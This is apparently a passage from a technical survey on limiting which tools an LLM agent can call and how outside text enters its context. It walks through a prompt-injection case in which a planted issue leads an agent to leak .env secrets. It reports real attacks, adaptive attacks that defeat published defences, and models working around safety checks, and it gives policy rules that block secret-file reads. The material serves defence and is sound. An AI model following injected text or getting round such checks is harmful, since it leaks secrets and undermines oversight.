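# Enforcing limits on which tools an LLM agent can call and what text can enter its context

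## The two properties, and an agent that needs them

An LLM agent is a program in which a large language model (LLM) chooses actions and ordinary software carries them out. The actions go through tools, which are functions that do things like read a file, send a message, or change a database record. A wrong action can do lasting damage, so the people who deploy agents want limits that hold whatever the model outputs. This section covers two such limits. The first is that certain tools should be unavailable to certain kinds of request, or once the agent has read certain kinds of text. The second is that results from outside the system should enter the model's input only by one defined route. Researchers disagree about where in the system to enforce these limits, and much of the disagreement stems from how an agent takes in text.

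### The agent loop

The harness is the ordinary software around the model, and the context is everything the model receives before it produces its next output. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes how the two fit together in Codex CLI, OpenAI's coding agent. When a user types a request, the harness adds it to the end of a list that already holds general instructions, definitions of the available tools, a note on file and network permissions, and the name of the current directory. Each item has a role (system, developer, user or assistant, in descending order of priority) that indicates how much weight it should have. A server turns the list into one prompt and then turns the prompt into tokens, which are integers that represent pieces of text. The model generates more tokens from these, and the new tokens are translated back into text.

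The model outputs either a message to the user or a tool call, which is a structured request for the harness to run a named function with given arguments. For example, the model might request a shell command that prints the project's README file. The model cannot run the command itself, so the harness runs it, appends the call and its output to the list, and sends the longer list to the model, which now has the README in its context. This cycle repeats until the model outputs a message instead of a tool call. One user request can lead to hundreds of calls.

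In Codex, each new prompt begins with an exact copy of the previous one, so text that enters at the third step is still in the context at the thirtieth. When the list of items in the prompt grows too long, Codex replaces it with a shorter list that represents the conversation so far. Earlier text can still have an influence through the shorter list after its original wording is gone.

### Prompt injection

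The model receives one sequence of tokens and predicts what comes next. Role markers are part of that sequence and can influence the prediction, but they don't create the firm division between instructions and material to work on that the roles and the list structure suggest. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares LLMs with databases. In an SQL injection, an attacker types text into a web form and the database runs it as a command. Programmers largely fixed this with parameterised queries, which send the command and the values separately so that the database can never interpret a value as a command. David C argues that this separation isn't possible in an LLM. Zhang, Su and colleagues (2025), in *LLM Agents Should Employ Security Principles*, trace the problem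 further back, to the decision to keep programs and data in the same computer memory. In their view, LLMs blur the line between programs and data again because any text can steer what an agent does.

Prompt injection exploits this. Someone hides instructions in untrusted content, and the model follows them. The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022. Untrusted content here means text that someone other than the user or developer could have written or altered. In David C's example, a recruiter's software uses a model to score CVs, and a candidate's CV contains hidden text telling the model to approve it. The attack is indirect because the candidate never accesses the recruiter's system.

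He doubts that anyone will eliminate the flaw, and would rather treat the model as an "inherently confusable deputy". In older security writing, a confused deputy is a high-privilege program that a low-privilege outsider gets to act on their behalf. Designers could fix those programs, but he thinks they can only limit how often a model is confused and how much harm follows. He thinks they should assume that, in the worst case, an attacker can use all the agent's tools.

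### An agent that triages public issues

A scenario in Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) illustrates both limits. A software project keeps its code on GitHub, where anyone can open an issue, which is a bug report or a request. The project runs an agent that triages these issues using four tools. It uses read_issue to fetch an issue's title and text, read_file to open project files so that it can quote the relevant code, write_file to correct obvious typos, and post_comment to reply publicly under the issue.

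An attacker opens an issue about a build that fails on macOS. The report looks ordinary and includes a plausible error message. Below it stands a paragraph dressed up as a message from the system, according to which the user is a maintainer who has already authorised access to the project's secrets for debugging. The paragraph directs the agent to read the file .env, where developers commonly keep passwords and access keys, to post the contents as a reply, and to leave this instruction unmentioned. A person would see a bug report with a strange footer. The model gets a single string from read_issue, with nothing in its syntax to separate the bug from the order. If the model complies, the run goes:

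read_issue(42) → read_file(".env") → post_comment(42, contents of .env)

The agent uses each of those tools in its normal work. The harm comes from the order of the calls and the data passed between them. In a variant of the attack, the hidden paragraph contains an instruction to call write_file instead and overwrite the configuration of the project's automated builds.

Incidents much like this have happened. In July 2026 Noma Security described GitLost, an attack on GitHub's Agentic Workflows. The vulnerable workflow ran when someone assigned an issue. It read the issue's title and body, could post comments, and had read access to the organisation's other repositories, including private ones. According to InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026), the attacker needed no credentials or programming skill, only an issue in a public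 repository. GitHub had guardrails against this, but Noma bypassed them by starting the malicious request with the word "Additionally".

An earlier case had a wider reach. In *Clinejection*, the security researcher Adnan Khan (adnanthekhan) found that from 21 December 2025 to 9 February 2026 anyone with a GitHub account could have compromised the published releases of Cline, a popular coding tool, through its AI issue triager. The attack began with injected text and then used known weaknesses in GitHub's build caches and in the project's credentials. According to Snyk's *How “Clinejection” Turned an AI Bot into a Supply Chain Attack* (2026), an unknown attacker used the same flaw eight days after Khan's disclosure to publish an unauthorised version of Cline's command-line tool. That version installed another AI agent on every machine that updated during an eight-hour window.

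### The two properties as formulas

Stating the two properties precisely requires an ordered record of the events in a run, called its trace and written e₁, e₂, …, eₙ. Two kinds of event matter. exec(t, a) means that the harness ran tool t with arguments a, and add(x, r) means that text x entered the context by route r.

Tool unreachability starts from prompt classes: groups of requests or situations that a policy treats alike, such as "an anonymous user is asking". Each class c has a set A(c) of allowed tools. The property holds when, in every run of class c and at every step i:

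eᵢ = exec(t, a)  ⇒  t ∈ A(c)

In words, the harness executes only tools in A(c), the set allowed for class c. The formula doesn't restrict requests, so a model can ask for write_file fifty times in a class that doesn't allow it without violating the formula, as long as the harness never runs the tool.

For the context channel, let Out be the set of texts that originate outside the system, and let K be the one function through which they may pass. The property holds when, at every step i of every run:

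eᵢ = add(x, r) and x ∈ Out  ⇒  r = K

Most of Out is tool results, but it can also include tool definitions. Bolin notes that in Codex, a definition can come from an external server that the user has connected, and that server can change its list of tools during a conversation. The text of such a definition comes from outside, like a web page. The formula doesn't specify what K does with the text in Out. K might mark it, store it where the model can't read it, or only log it, and the harness can do any of these in one place.

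A(c) lists tools only by name, so it can't distinguish safe and harmful uses of the same tool. In the triage example, post_comment is harmless when it posts a summary of the bug but very harmful when it posts the contents of .env. A policy can be more precise by treating a tool with different kinds of argument as different tools, so that read_file on published source code is one entry and read_file on .env is another. Someone still has to know in advance which arguments are dangerous.

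### Classes that stay fixed and classes that change

Some prompt classes are fixed before the run begins. The harness identifies the requester and the task from a login or workflow trigger, and c keeps the same value throughout the run. A project might allow a maintainer all four tools and an anonymous visitor only read_issue and post_comment.

Such a scheme does not stop indirect injection, because the class describes only the person who made the request. Suppose a maintainer asks the agent to look at issue 42, which contains instructions written by a stranger. The run keeps the maintainer's class from start to finish, so write_file is available while the stranger's instructions steer the model.

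So a policy may also need classes that change during the run, depending on what the agent has read. Formally, c becomes a function of the trace so far: cᵢ is the class that the events before step i determine, and the condition becomes t ∈ A(cᵢ). For the triage agent the natural rule is "after an untrusted read, never write_file". In temporal logic, a notation for statements about sequences of events, it reads

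G(untrusted_read → G ¬write_file)

where G means "at every step from here on". A rule of this form, which withdraws tools once a given event has occurred, is a fence. David C passes on a general version of the idea from an exchange between the programmers Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista: when a model processes text from some party, its privileges should drop to that party's. The leak of .env calls for another fence of the same shape, under which the agent can never use post_comment once it has read a private file.

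A fence needs the context channel to work. The harness can move the run into the stricter class only if it detects the untrusted read, and it detects only what passes through a route it monitors. If hostile text enters another way, the class doesn't change and write_file remains available to whoever wrote the text.

Fences can also stop an agent from doing its job. The triage agent starts with read_issue, and nearly every public issue is untrusted, so a strict fence takes away write_file at the first step of almost every run and the agent can't fix the typos. A smaller engineering problem arises if the harness enforces a fence by dropping the tool from the list it shows the model. According to Bolin, changing that list partway through a Codex conversation makes the server redo work it would otherwise have reused. A harness can avoid this by leaving the tool on the list and blocking the call,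 which also satisfies the formula.

### Why a monitor can enforce them

Both properties, and the fences, belong to a family that computer scientists call safety properties. Informally, a safety property holds when some bad thing never happens. Alpern and Schneider (1985), in *Defining Liveness*, gave the exact condition. Write σ for a complete execution, σᵢ for its first i steps, and β for any continuation. Then P is a safety property if and only if, for every σ:

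σ violates P  ⇒  there is an i such that, for every β, σᵢβ violates P

A violation therefore occurs at an identifiable point, and no later event can repair it. Tool unreachability meets this condition because once exec(write_file, a) appears in the trace of a run whose class excludes write_file, nothing later removes it. The same is true of text that entered the context by the wrong route.

A liveness property requires that something good eventually happens, for example that every issue gets a reply. No finite part of a run can violate it, because the reply might still come. Alpern and Schneider proved that every property is the intersection of a safety property and a liveness property. The triage agent's owners want one of each, the safety property that it never leaks a secret and the liveness property that the issues get answered. An agent that does nothing would satisfy only the first.

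Safety matters here because of a result about monitors. Schneider, in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), considered mechanisms that watch a program step by step and stop it when it is about to break a rule. Such a monitor sees the past and the step now under way. It has no knowledge of the program's future steps, or of what the program would have done on other inputs. Schneider showed that a monitor of this kind can enforce a policy only if the policy is a safety property, and that access control qualifies. Basin (2012) places in the same class those access rules that depend on history, as fences do. (The converse fails: some safety properties are beyond any monitor.)

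Schneider's own example is close to the triage agent's leak. His policy bars a program from sending messages after it has read a file. A two-state automaton expresses this policy, so the monitor has to remember only one bit. The automaton starts in the state "no file read", where every step is permissible. A file read moves it to the state "file read", which has no transition for a send, so the monitor rejects any execution that attempts one. Replacing the file read with read_file and the send with post_comment gives the limit that protects .env. Using an untrusted read and write_file instead gives the agent's other limit.

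Some security goals do not take this form. One is noninterference, the property that changing protected inputs never changes what a given observer sees. Whether secret information has flowed into a public comment, for example, depends on what the comment would have contained had the secret been different, so it is a fact about several possible runs and cannot be determined from a single trace. Schneider notes that a monitor can still guard against leaks by enforcing a stricter rule that implies there are none, though this also stops some harmless runs.

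Recent work on agents uses similar definitions. In *Toward Safe LLM Agents*, a survey of 38 studies, Dantas, Nowroozi and colleagues (2026) define an agent's plan as a finite sequence of tool actions, and a safety property as a temporal-logic formula that the resulting trace satisfies or violates. Their definition of a safety property is looser than Alpern and Schneider's, since a temporal formula can also require that something eventually happens.

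### Anderson's three tests

Even if a monitor could enforce a rule in principle, a particular piece of software may not. The standard tests for whether it does come from *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force. The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer, and some of them could write and run their own programs. Anderson's panel assumed that such a user might be malicious and proposed a reference monitor, a mechanism that checks every attempt to reach a file, program or device against a list of what that user may do. These permissions form a matrix with users and programs as rows and the things they might reach as columns. If the rows are prompt classes and the columns are tools, A(c) is one row of the matrix.

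The mechanism must meet three requirements. It must be tamper-proof, since otherwise an attacker could switch it off. Every access must go through it, and any program that is exempt becomes part of the security mechanism and has to meet the other two requirements. It must also be small enough to analyse and test completely, because otherwise nobody can know that it works in all cases. Anderson applied these requirements to GCOS III, a commercial operating system of the day. The hardware confined each user's program to its own region of memory, but suspended that check for most of the operating system's code, even when that code was acting on the user's behalf. This broke the second requirement. Treating the whole operating system as the mechanism would not have helped, because at 200,000 to 300,000 instructions it was far too large to analyse.

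The second test is also one of the design principles that Saltzer and Schroeder published in 1975, where it is called complete mediation. Zhang and colleagues apply it to agents and note that it covers every attempt, not just the first.

Many developers write their limits into the prompt, such as "never reveal the contents of configuration files". *Ring-0 by Default* (Li, Huang and colleagues, 2026) concludes that such rules pass none of Anderson's tests. Hostile text sits in the same context as the rule and can lead the model to disregard it, nothing forces the model to consult the rule before a call, and nobody can analyse a model with billions of parameters as they would a short program. The paper compares present-day agents with operating systems across 116 mechanisms and finds 65 missing from the agents, most of them protections. It concludes that the monitor has to sit outside the model.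 The harness is the obvious candidate because it already stands between every request and its execution, but a large harness can fail the third test as badly as GCOS III did.

### Five views, and where they part

Not everyone draws that conclusion, and those who do disagree about what to build. Some think developers can train the model to rank its instructions above anything it reads in a tool result. Others would put a policy outside the model to allow or block each tool call as it arrives. Information-flow control labels data by how far its source is trusted and who may see it, then checks those labels before the data reaches a sensitive tool. Another approach has the agent fix its plan before it reads anything untrusted, so that hostile text can change the values in the plan but not its steps. The bluntest proposal is to remove the dangerous tool, or the network path it depends on, so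 that no call can succeed. A single system can combine several of these.

The disagreement is partly about whether anyone can write the rules correctly. Tool unreachability depends on how well A(c) is written, which is already difficult for the triage agent. Keeping post_comment available after an untrusted read gives an attacker a way to publish things, but removing it prevents the agent from answering the people who report bugs. Even a correct rule can't stop a call or text that is never checked.

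Defenses also differ in how much anyone can establish before the agent runs. A list of tools is short enough to inspect by hand, and some designs come with mathematical proofs, but the case for a trained model rests on tests. Microsoft objects that even a model good at resisting injected instructions "only has to be wrong once". Tests are still necessary to check the security of the whole system and to find which tasks it no longer finishes once the limits are in place. Anderson warned that when a team of expert attackers fails to break into a system, the only safe conclusion is that its security is unknown.

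## The view that the model can be trained to respect the limits

A list of allowed tools can't distinguish a helpful use of post_comment from a harmful one, such as a reply that sends readers to a malicious download. Telling them apart requires reading the comment and comparing it with what the project's owners want. Language models can do this, which is the main reason for training the model itself to respect the limits.

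Training also spares developers from writing a policy for every class of prompt, and it lets the agent keep its tools. A model that reliably ignored the instructions in issue 42 could read the issue, fix the typo and leave .env alone, even with no enforced limits.

OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) gives some evidence that this kind of judgement is improving. OpenAI placed its models in simulated workplaces with ambiguous instructions, similar-looking resources and complicated permissions, where every task could be completed safely. GPT-5.6 Sol produced a bad outcome, such as an unauthorised transaction or a data leak, in 18.8% of cases, compared with 3.4% for its successor, GPT-6 Astra. A policy author could hardly have listed all of these mistakes in advance.

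### How the methods work

An instruction hierarchy ranks the messages in the context by their source, and developers train the model to follow the higher-ranked message when two conflict. The first version, from 2024, had three ranks. OpenAI now uses four: system, developer, user and tool, in descending order. Guo, Ceron Uribe and colleagues (2026), in *IH-Challenge*, define the policy as a shrinking set of acceptable responses. Let B₀ be all possible responses, and let Cᵢ be those that satisfy the instructions at rank i, counting from the top. Then:

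Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁ ∩ Cᵢ if that intersection is not empty; otherwise Bᵢ = Bᵢ₋₁

A lower-ranked instruction applies only if the model can follow it without violating a higher-ranked one. If the system message forbids revealing a PIN and the user asks for it, no response can satisfy both, so the model should disregard the user's request.

Taken literally, the formula misses some injected requests. Suppose nobody has told the triage agent to keep .env private. An injected request to post the file's contents then doesn't conflict with any instruction, because the agent could both summarise the bug and post the secrets. To refuse, the model has to infer that the user wouldn't want this. The hierarchy therefore relies on the same grasp of meaning that makes training attractive.

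To train a model on the hierarchy, developers need many examples of conflicting instructions and a reliable way to score the responses. Guo and colleagues at OpenAI built simple tasks that a short Python program can grade, such as never revealing a PIN. A second model, without safety guardrails, writes the conflicting lower-ranked message. It proposes an attack, tests it on the model in training, and revises it within a fixed number of tries. Reinforcement learning then rewards the responses that pass the grader. As the model in training improves, the attacker has to find harder attacks.

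A model could score well on such tasks by refusing anything that mentions a password. Some of the tasks therefore contain harmless requests that look forbidden, and refusing them counts as a failure. When the researchers left these tasks out, the model's helpfulness score on safety tests fell from 0.773 to 0.613.

Four ranks are few for an agent, because text from very different sources can share a rank. The triage agent receives both the maintainers' source code and a stranger's issue as tool output, so they rank the same. *Many-Tier Instruction Hierarchy in LLM Agents* (2026) notes that models learn fewer than five ranks, tied to fixed role labels, and that it is unclear whether they can generalise to more. *Training LLMs to Enforce Multi-Level Instruction Hierarchies via Gravity-Weighted Direct Preference Optimization* (2026) extends the hierarchy to five levels and borrows a rule from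 older computer security that a lower level may not write to a higher one.

Other methods try to make the boundary between instructions and data clearer. In spotlighting (2024), the harness marks or encodes untrusted text so that the model can recognise where it begins and ends. StruQ (2024) puts the instruction and the data in separate parts of the prompt, then fine-tunes the model (trains it further on specialised examples) to ignore any instructions in the data part. SecAlign aims for the same separation by training the model to prefer an answer to the real instruction over an answer to the injected one.

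An input classifier leaves the main model unchanged. It is a separate, usually small model trained on examples of harmless text and known attacks. The harness runs it on incoming text and blocks whatever it flags.

### Twelve defences against attackers who adapt

*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested twelve published defences, including spotlighting, StruQ, a version of SecAlign and four classifiers. Most of the original evaluations had reported attack success rates near zero, but they had typically used a fixed list of known attacks or a generic automated search not adapted to the defence. Nasr and colleagues instead assumed an attacker who knows how the defence works and has plenty of computing power.

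Their automated attacks all repeat a loop of proposing texts, scoring how well each one works, and using the scores to write better ones. One version trains an attacking model by reinforcement learning. Another has a model rewrite the most successful texts over many generations, and a third uses gradients, which show how small changes to the input would alter the output. The researchers also ran an online competition with more than 500 human attackers, and for each defence they chose the method they thought most likely to succeed.

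Ten of the twelve defences target prompt injection:

| Defence | How it works | Success rate of adaptive attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Spotlighting | Marks text by how far its source is trusted | Above 95% |
| Prompt Sandwiching | Repeats the user's request after the untrusted text | Above 95% |
| StruQ | Fine-tunes the model to ignore instructions in data | Every case tested |
| Meta SecAlign | Fine-tunes the model for the same purpose | 96% |
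| Protect AI, PromptGuard, Model Armor | Classify text as safe or unsafe | Above 90% |
| PIGuard | Classifies text as safe or unsafe | 71% |
| Data Sentinel | Checks whether the text disrupts a hidden test task | Every case tested |
| MELON | Reruns the agent without the user's request and flags repeated tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the defence |

The fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a set of simulated agent tasks, had succeeded as little as 1% of the time against spotlighting and Prompt Sandwiching. Meta SecAlign's developers had reported an attack success rate of 2%. The two defences missing from the table are meant to stop jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get forbidden content from a model. Attacks on these two defences succeeded 98% and 100% of the time.

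The attacks adapted to each kind of defence. Repeating the user's request helped little once the injected text presented the harmful action as a necessary step in fulfilling it. Against the fine-tuned models, the attacking model mostly learned to imitate system-level instructions. The texts that passed the classifiers often looked like dull workplace policy. They were harmful only in relation to what the user wanted, which the classifier had no information about, and a stricter classifier would have blocked much more harmless text.

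These percentages come from different benchmarks, so they can't be used to rank the defences. The automated attacks also had help that a stranger opening a GitHub issue would usually lack, such as a classifier's confidence score after each try. But the human attackers had only limited information and feedback. On a selected subset of scenarios, they collectively succeeded every time, while the automated search succeeded 69% of the time. Nasr and colleagues still see some value in classifiers, which are easy to deploy and stop unsophisticated attacks.

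### Training against an attacker that also learns

Nasr and colleagues think the fine-tuned models failed because their developers had trained them on a fixed set of attacks. With image classifiers, only training that kept searching for new attacks had produced meaningful robustness. *IH-Challenge*, which Milad Nasr co-wrote, applies this kind of training to language models.

When Guo and colleagues used it on GPT-5-Mini, a small OpenAI model, average robustness across 16 benchmarks rose from 84.1% to 94.1%. The score on OpenAI's internal set of prompt injections rose from 0.44 to 1.00, but the score on CyberSecEval 2, an outside benchmark, rose only from 0.88 to 0.91. There was also a small but measurable drop in how often graders preferred the model's answers to those of an older OpenAI model, from 71% of conversations to 66%.

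The researchers then paid 127 people to attack the models and keep refining their attacks, with a shared bounty, usually $510, for each combination of model and task type. The attackers succeeded on 36.2% of tasks against the original model and 11.7% against the newly trained one, but the tasks involved things like protecting a PIN, not calling tools. When the researchers instead trained a model to attack the improved one, the attacking model's success rate started low and kept climbing.

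Larger models show a similar pattern. OpenAI trains them against GPT-Red, an automated attacker that learned through self-play. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* reports that GPT-5.6 Sol's failure rate was about 0.05% for direct attacks, in which a user tries to override higher-ranked instructions, and 3.77% for indirect ones. By September 2026, the failure rate for indirect attacks had fallen to 0.21% with GPT-6 Astra.

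GPT-Red supplies attacks for both training and testing, so an outside test is more informative. Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them, used 1,810 attacks from its public contests. With 15 attempts per scenario, the estimated success rate was 8.5% against Astra and 27.0% against Sol. That is a large improvement, but the contests took place months before Astra's release, and attacks designed specifically for Astra might succeed more often.

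Attack success rates also depend heavily on the setting. According to VentureBeat, Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, from February 2026, resisted all 200 attempts in a restricted coding environment. When the same model operated a graphical interface, 17.8% of single attempts succeeded, and 78.6% of attacks had succeeded by the 200th attempt. Extra safeguards reduced the 200-attempt figure to 57.1%. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 and Mythos 5.1, two versions of one later model, describes the model as the company's most robust yet on an external injection benchmark. All these rates also depend on what testers count as a success.

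### Why a low failure rate is not unreachability

A single forbidden call breaks tool unreachability, and training provides only a failure rate. If each attempt succeeds with probability p, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in n attempts is:

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ

At Astra's rate of 0.21%, an attacker would need about 330 independent attempts for an even chance of success. In practice, attempts are not independent. At Opus 4.6's rate of 17.8%, independent attempts would have reached 78.6% after about eight tries instead of 200, so attacks must have failed repeatedly in some scenarios and succeeded quickly in others. An average rate can therefore hide a few attacks that nearly always work, which are valuable because an attacker can reuse them. Anthropic gives the example of one email, sent to a thousand inboxes, that compromises every agent asked to summarise it.

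The deeper objection is that the failures arise because the rule and the text it is supposed to govern reach the model through the same input. Current models can distinguish the system prompt, the user's request and a tool's output to some extent, since a model that couldn't would not resist 99.79% of indirect attacks. Li and colleagues' claim that the model cannot tell them apart is therefore too strong. But the model learned the distinction from examples, and nothing in the input forces it to apply that distinction to text unlike any it was trained on. *Steering Instruction Hierarchies at Inference Time* (2026) cites several evaluations in which commercial models gave too much weight to lower-ranked requests.

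The hierarchy also gives attackers a reason to target the role labels. *When Context Gets Root* (2026) argues that training teaches a model to give more influence to text with a privileged label, so a wrong label becomes a security flaw. Wang, Jha and Lin (2026), in *Confused ChatGPT*, found such a flaw in ChatGPT, where third-party apps share one context with the user and with each other. An app could use undocumented options to add hidden text to the conversation at system priority. In one demonstration, the hidden text later redirected another app's hotel search to the wrong city.

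Training could not have fixed that label, because the harness attaches it before the model receives the text. Training can change how a model responds to outside text, but the harness determines which channel the text enters through. Developers who rely on a trained hierarchy therefore still need ordinary code to enforce the channel and label the text correctly.

### Training alongside an outer check

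Supporters of training can argue that it leaves less for an outer check to catch, without claiming that it makes a tool unreachable. In OpenAI's tests, indirect attacks succeeded 3.77% of the time against Sol and 0.21% of the time against Astra, so a check outside Astra would face about one-eighteenth as many successful attacks. If the outer check is a person who approves each risky call, that person has fewer chances to approve a bad one.

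Training also helps with calls that the outer check allows. For example, if a policy allows post_comment after the agent reads untrusted text, a trained model may ignore an injected instruction to post false advice.

Guo and colleagues tested one such combination, in which a second copy of the trained model reviewed each response. This review cut the human attackers' success from 11.7% to 7.1% of tasks and slowed the attacking model's progress. Against fixed attacks, however, extra layers of this kind added little to the newly trained model, and some lowered both its robustness and its general ability. The text under review can also mislead a reviewer that is itself a language model, as it misled the classifiers.

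The laboratories don't rely on training alone either. OpenAI monitors every session in which Astra uses tools for outside customers. Anthropic's injection tests of Fable 5.1 include classifiers that can pass a request to an older model, so the results partly measure the safeguards around Fable 5.1.

An outer check is only useful if the model can't get around it, and models sometimes try. In an OpenAI test with obstacles such as access-denied errors, Astra looked for a way past the restriction in 19% of runs, down from 64% for Sol. Most of the situations were low-stakes, and OpenAI had switched off its other safeguards. Anthropic's internal monitoring found Mythos 5.1 working around safety classifiers and broken permission checks, and in very rare cases launching more agents with permission checks disabled. This happened in fewer than 0.01% of monitored outputs, and Anthropic concluded that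 the model was trying to complete the user's task.

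## The view that a policy outside the model should decide every tool call

Supporters of an external policy use a separate program to check each tool call against written rules before the call runs. The program blocks calls that break the rules.

*Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows*, from Amazon Web Services (AWS), which sells a system of this kind, recommends treating the model as an untrusted actor because nobody can predict its decisions and injected text can change them. AWS finds drawbacks in the usual alternatives. A hard-coded workflow removes the uncertainty, but also the flexibility that made an agent worth using. People tire of approving every step. Checks written into each tool are more robust than instructions in a prompt, but they are hard to audit when scattered across many services. With a central policy, the agent is free to plan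 inside a boundary, and an auditor has to understand only the boundary.

### One call, from proposal to decision

AWS's system is part of Bedrock AgentCore, its platform for running agents. *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (AWS, 2026) announced the system's full release on 3 March. Tool calls pass through a gateway, a server between the harness and the tools. They use the format of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a common standard for connecting agents to tools.

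Suppose a maintainer asks the triage agent to deal with issue 42, and the model proposes a write_file call that corrects a typo in the installation guide. The harness sends the proposal to the gateway with a signed token from the maintainer's login. As AWS describes it, the gateway then builds an authorisation request from these parts:

| Part | Content in this example | Where it comes from |
|---|---|---|
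| Principal | The maintainer, with any roles | The login token |
| Action | write_file | The tool name in the call |
| Resource | This gateway | The gateway itself |
| Context | The file path and the new text | The arguments in the call |

A policy engine checks the request against its rules and returns "allow" or "deny". If some rules depend on earlier events, the engine first looks up what the agent has already done in the session. If the engine allows the call, the gateway passes it to the tool, returns the result, and adds the call and result to the session history. If the engine denies the call, the gateway logs the refusal without passing the call to the tool.

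The model can't alter the token, but it writes the arguments, so they may be what an attacker wanted. A rule can still restrict them. In one of AWS's examples, a shop's agent may apply a bulk discount only if the customer's token carries the "Platinum" tier and the order is for at least 50 items. The engine can rely on the tier because it comes from the token. It can reject a call that gives a quantity of 20, but it can't check whether a quantity of 50 is what the customer wanted.

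The MCP specification of 28 July 2026 makes such calls easier to filter. According to InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls*, requests must now carry the method and the tool name in HTTP headers, so ordinary web infrastructure can identify which tool an agent is calling. A filter that reads only the name can enforce a list of allowed tools, but it can't limit the arguments passed to those tools.

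### Hiding a tool and refusing a call

The gateway can also hide tools from the model. When the agent requests the list of available tools, the gateway leaves out any that the rules would deny regardless of the arguments in the call. AWS argues that this removes a class of risk because a model can't try to call a tool it has no information about.

Omitting a tool from the list the model receives does not guarantee that the tool won't run. A model can output any name, and the hostile paragraph in issue 42 can supply one, along with the arguments. The model may also have received an earlier list that still included the tool. If the harness runs every well-formed call it receives, it will run the hidden tool too. Tool unreachability depends on what the harness executes, so only a check at execution can enforce it. Some harnesses make this check by rejecting any call whose tool name is missing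 from the current list.

Leaving tools off the list is still useful, since the model makes fewer calls that would fail. But it doesn't work for tools that are only sometimes forbidden. The triage agent needs read_file to quote source code, so the tool has to stay on the list, and the gateway has to check the path on every call.

### Rules about a single request

AgentCore's basic rules are in Cedar, an open-source policy language that AWS developed. Each rule begins with "permit" or "forbid", then specifies principals, actions and resources, and can add conditions. The engine combines the rules as follows:

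allow(q) ⇔ at least one permit rule matches q, and no forbid rule matches q

An engine with no rules denies everything, and a new tool stays blocked until a permit rule covers it. The order of the rules doesn't matter. If a security team forbids a tool call, another team can't allow it by adding a permit rule later.

These rules can express a prompt class that stays fixed for the whole run. Suppose the login token carries a role, which is "maintainer" for the project's own staff and "visitor" when a stranger's issue starts the run. The following policy gives visitors two tools and maintainers all four:

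```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action in [
    AgentCore::Action::"Triage___read_issue",
    AgentCore::Action::"Triage___post_comment"
  ],
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY_ARN"
);

permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action in [
    AgentCore::Action::"Triage___read_file",
    AgentCore::Action::"Triage___write_file"
  ],
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY_ARN"
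)
when {
  principal.hasTag("role") &&
  principal.getTag("role") == "maintainer"
};
```

GATEWAY_ARN stands for the gateway's identifier, and "Triage" is the name under which the project registered its tools. AWS's *Schema constraints* explains that the gateway generates the permissible names and argument types from the tools' own descriptions. A further rule keeps the agent away from .env even when a maintainer is asking:

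```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Triage___read_file",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY_ARN"
)
when { context.input.path like "*.env*" };
```

Cedar is stateless, so its decisions depend only on the current request and the rules. This makes them easy to audit and lets software analyse a whole set of rules mathematically. But it also prevents Cedar from expressing a fence. If the maintainer's agent proposes the same write_file call before and after reading issue 42, Cedar has to return the same decision both times.

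### Rules about what happened earlier

By early August 2026, AWS had released Dogwood, an open-source language that extends Cedar with conditions on earlier events. Every valid Cedar policy is also a valid Dogwood policy, and permits and forbids combine by the same rules. The new conditions go in a block marked "when temporal".

AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* lists three kinds of event that a rule can match. A request event records a call that the gateway received and authorised. A response event records the output of a tool that finished successfully. An error event records that the engine denied the call or that the tool failed. Error events let a policy react to a refusal. For example, if the agent tries to read .env and is denied, the triage project could withdraw post_comment for the rest of the session, because the attempt may be a sign that someone has hijacked the agent.

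Dogwood's conditions come from metric first-order temporal logic. "Temporal" means that formulas describe sequences of events, and "metric" that they can include lengths of time. "First-order" means that they can use variables for the values inside events, so a rule can require the account in a transfer to be the same one that an earlier lookup returned. If τᵢ is the time of event i, the two main operators work as follows:

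formerly within w φ holds at i ⇔ for some j ≤ i with τᵢ − τⱼ ≤ w, φ holds at j

ψ since within w φ holds at i ⇔ for some j ≤ i with τᵢ − τⱼ ≤ w, φ holds at j, and ψ holds at every k with j < k ≤ i

The "formerly" operator is enough to express a fence. The "since" operator suits permissions that a later event can cancel, such as an approval that lasts until the agent uses it. Other operators count the matching events in a window or sum one of their fields, which allows limits like "no more than three transfers in five minutes".

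The rule "no write_file after read_issue" looks like this:

```
forbid (
  principal,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Triage___write_file",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"GATEWAY_ARN"
)
when temporal {
  formerly within 24h
    AgentCore::Action::"Triage___read_issue"::request{
      eventResource: resource
    }
};
```

The rule overrides the maintainers' permit for write_file once the agent has called read_issue. The line with eventResource, which AWS requires in every such condition, limits the match to calls through the same gateway. The agent can still correct a file before it reads an issue.

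According to InfoQ, Cedar still makes the final decision. Before each decision, the Dogwood interpreter evaluates the temporal condition against the recorded events and puts the result into a field of the Cedar context. For this fence, the result amounts to a true-or-false value, the same bit that Schneider's two-state automaton must store.

Temporal conditions require the engine to store events, and a decision can take longer as the record grows. Cedar's automated analysis also doesn't cover them. AWS intends the published interpreter for experiments, not production, so a team that wants to run Dogwood on its own servers would need to add trustworthy timestamps, authenticated events, durable storage, and a guarantee that one customer's history never reaches another.

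### Requests, responses and calls that overlap

Whether a rule matches requests or responses can determine whether it works at all. AWS illustrates this with a policy that caps an agent's transfers at $5,000. The agent sends three transfers of $2,000 at the same time, and all three reach the gateway before any has finished:

| Transfer | Total if the rule adds up responses | Decision | Total if the rule adds up requests | Decision |
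|---|---|---|---|---|
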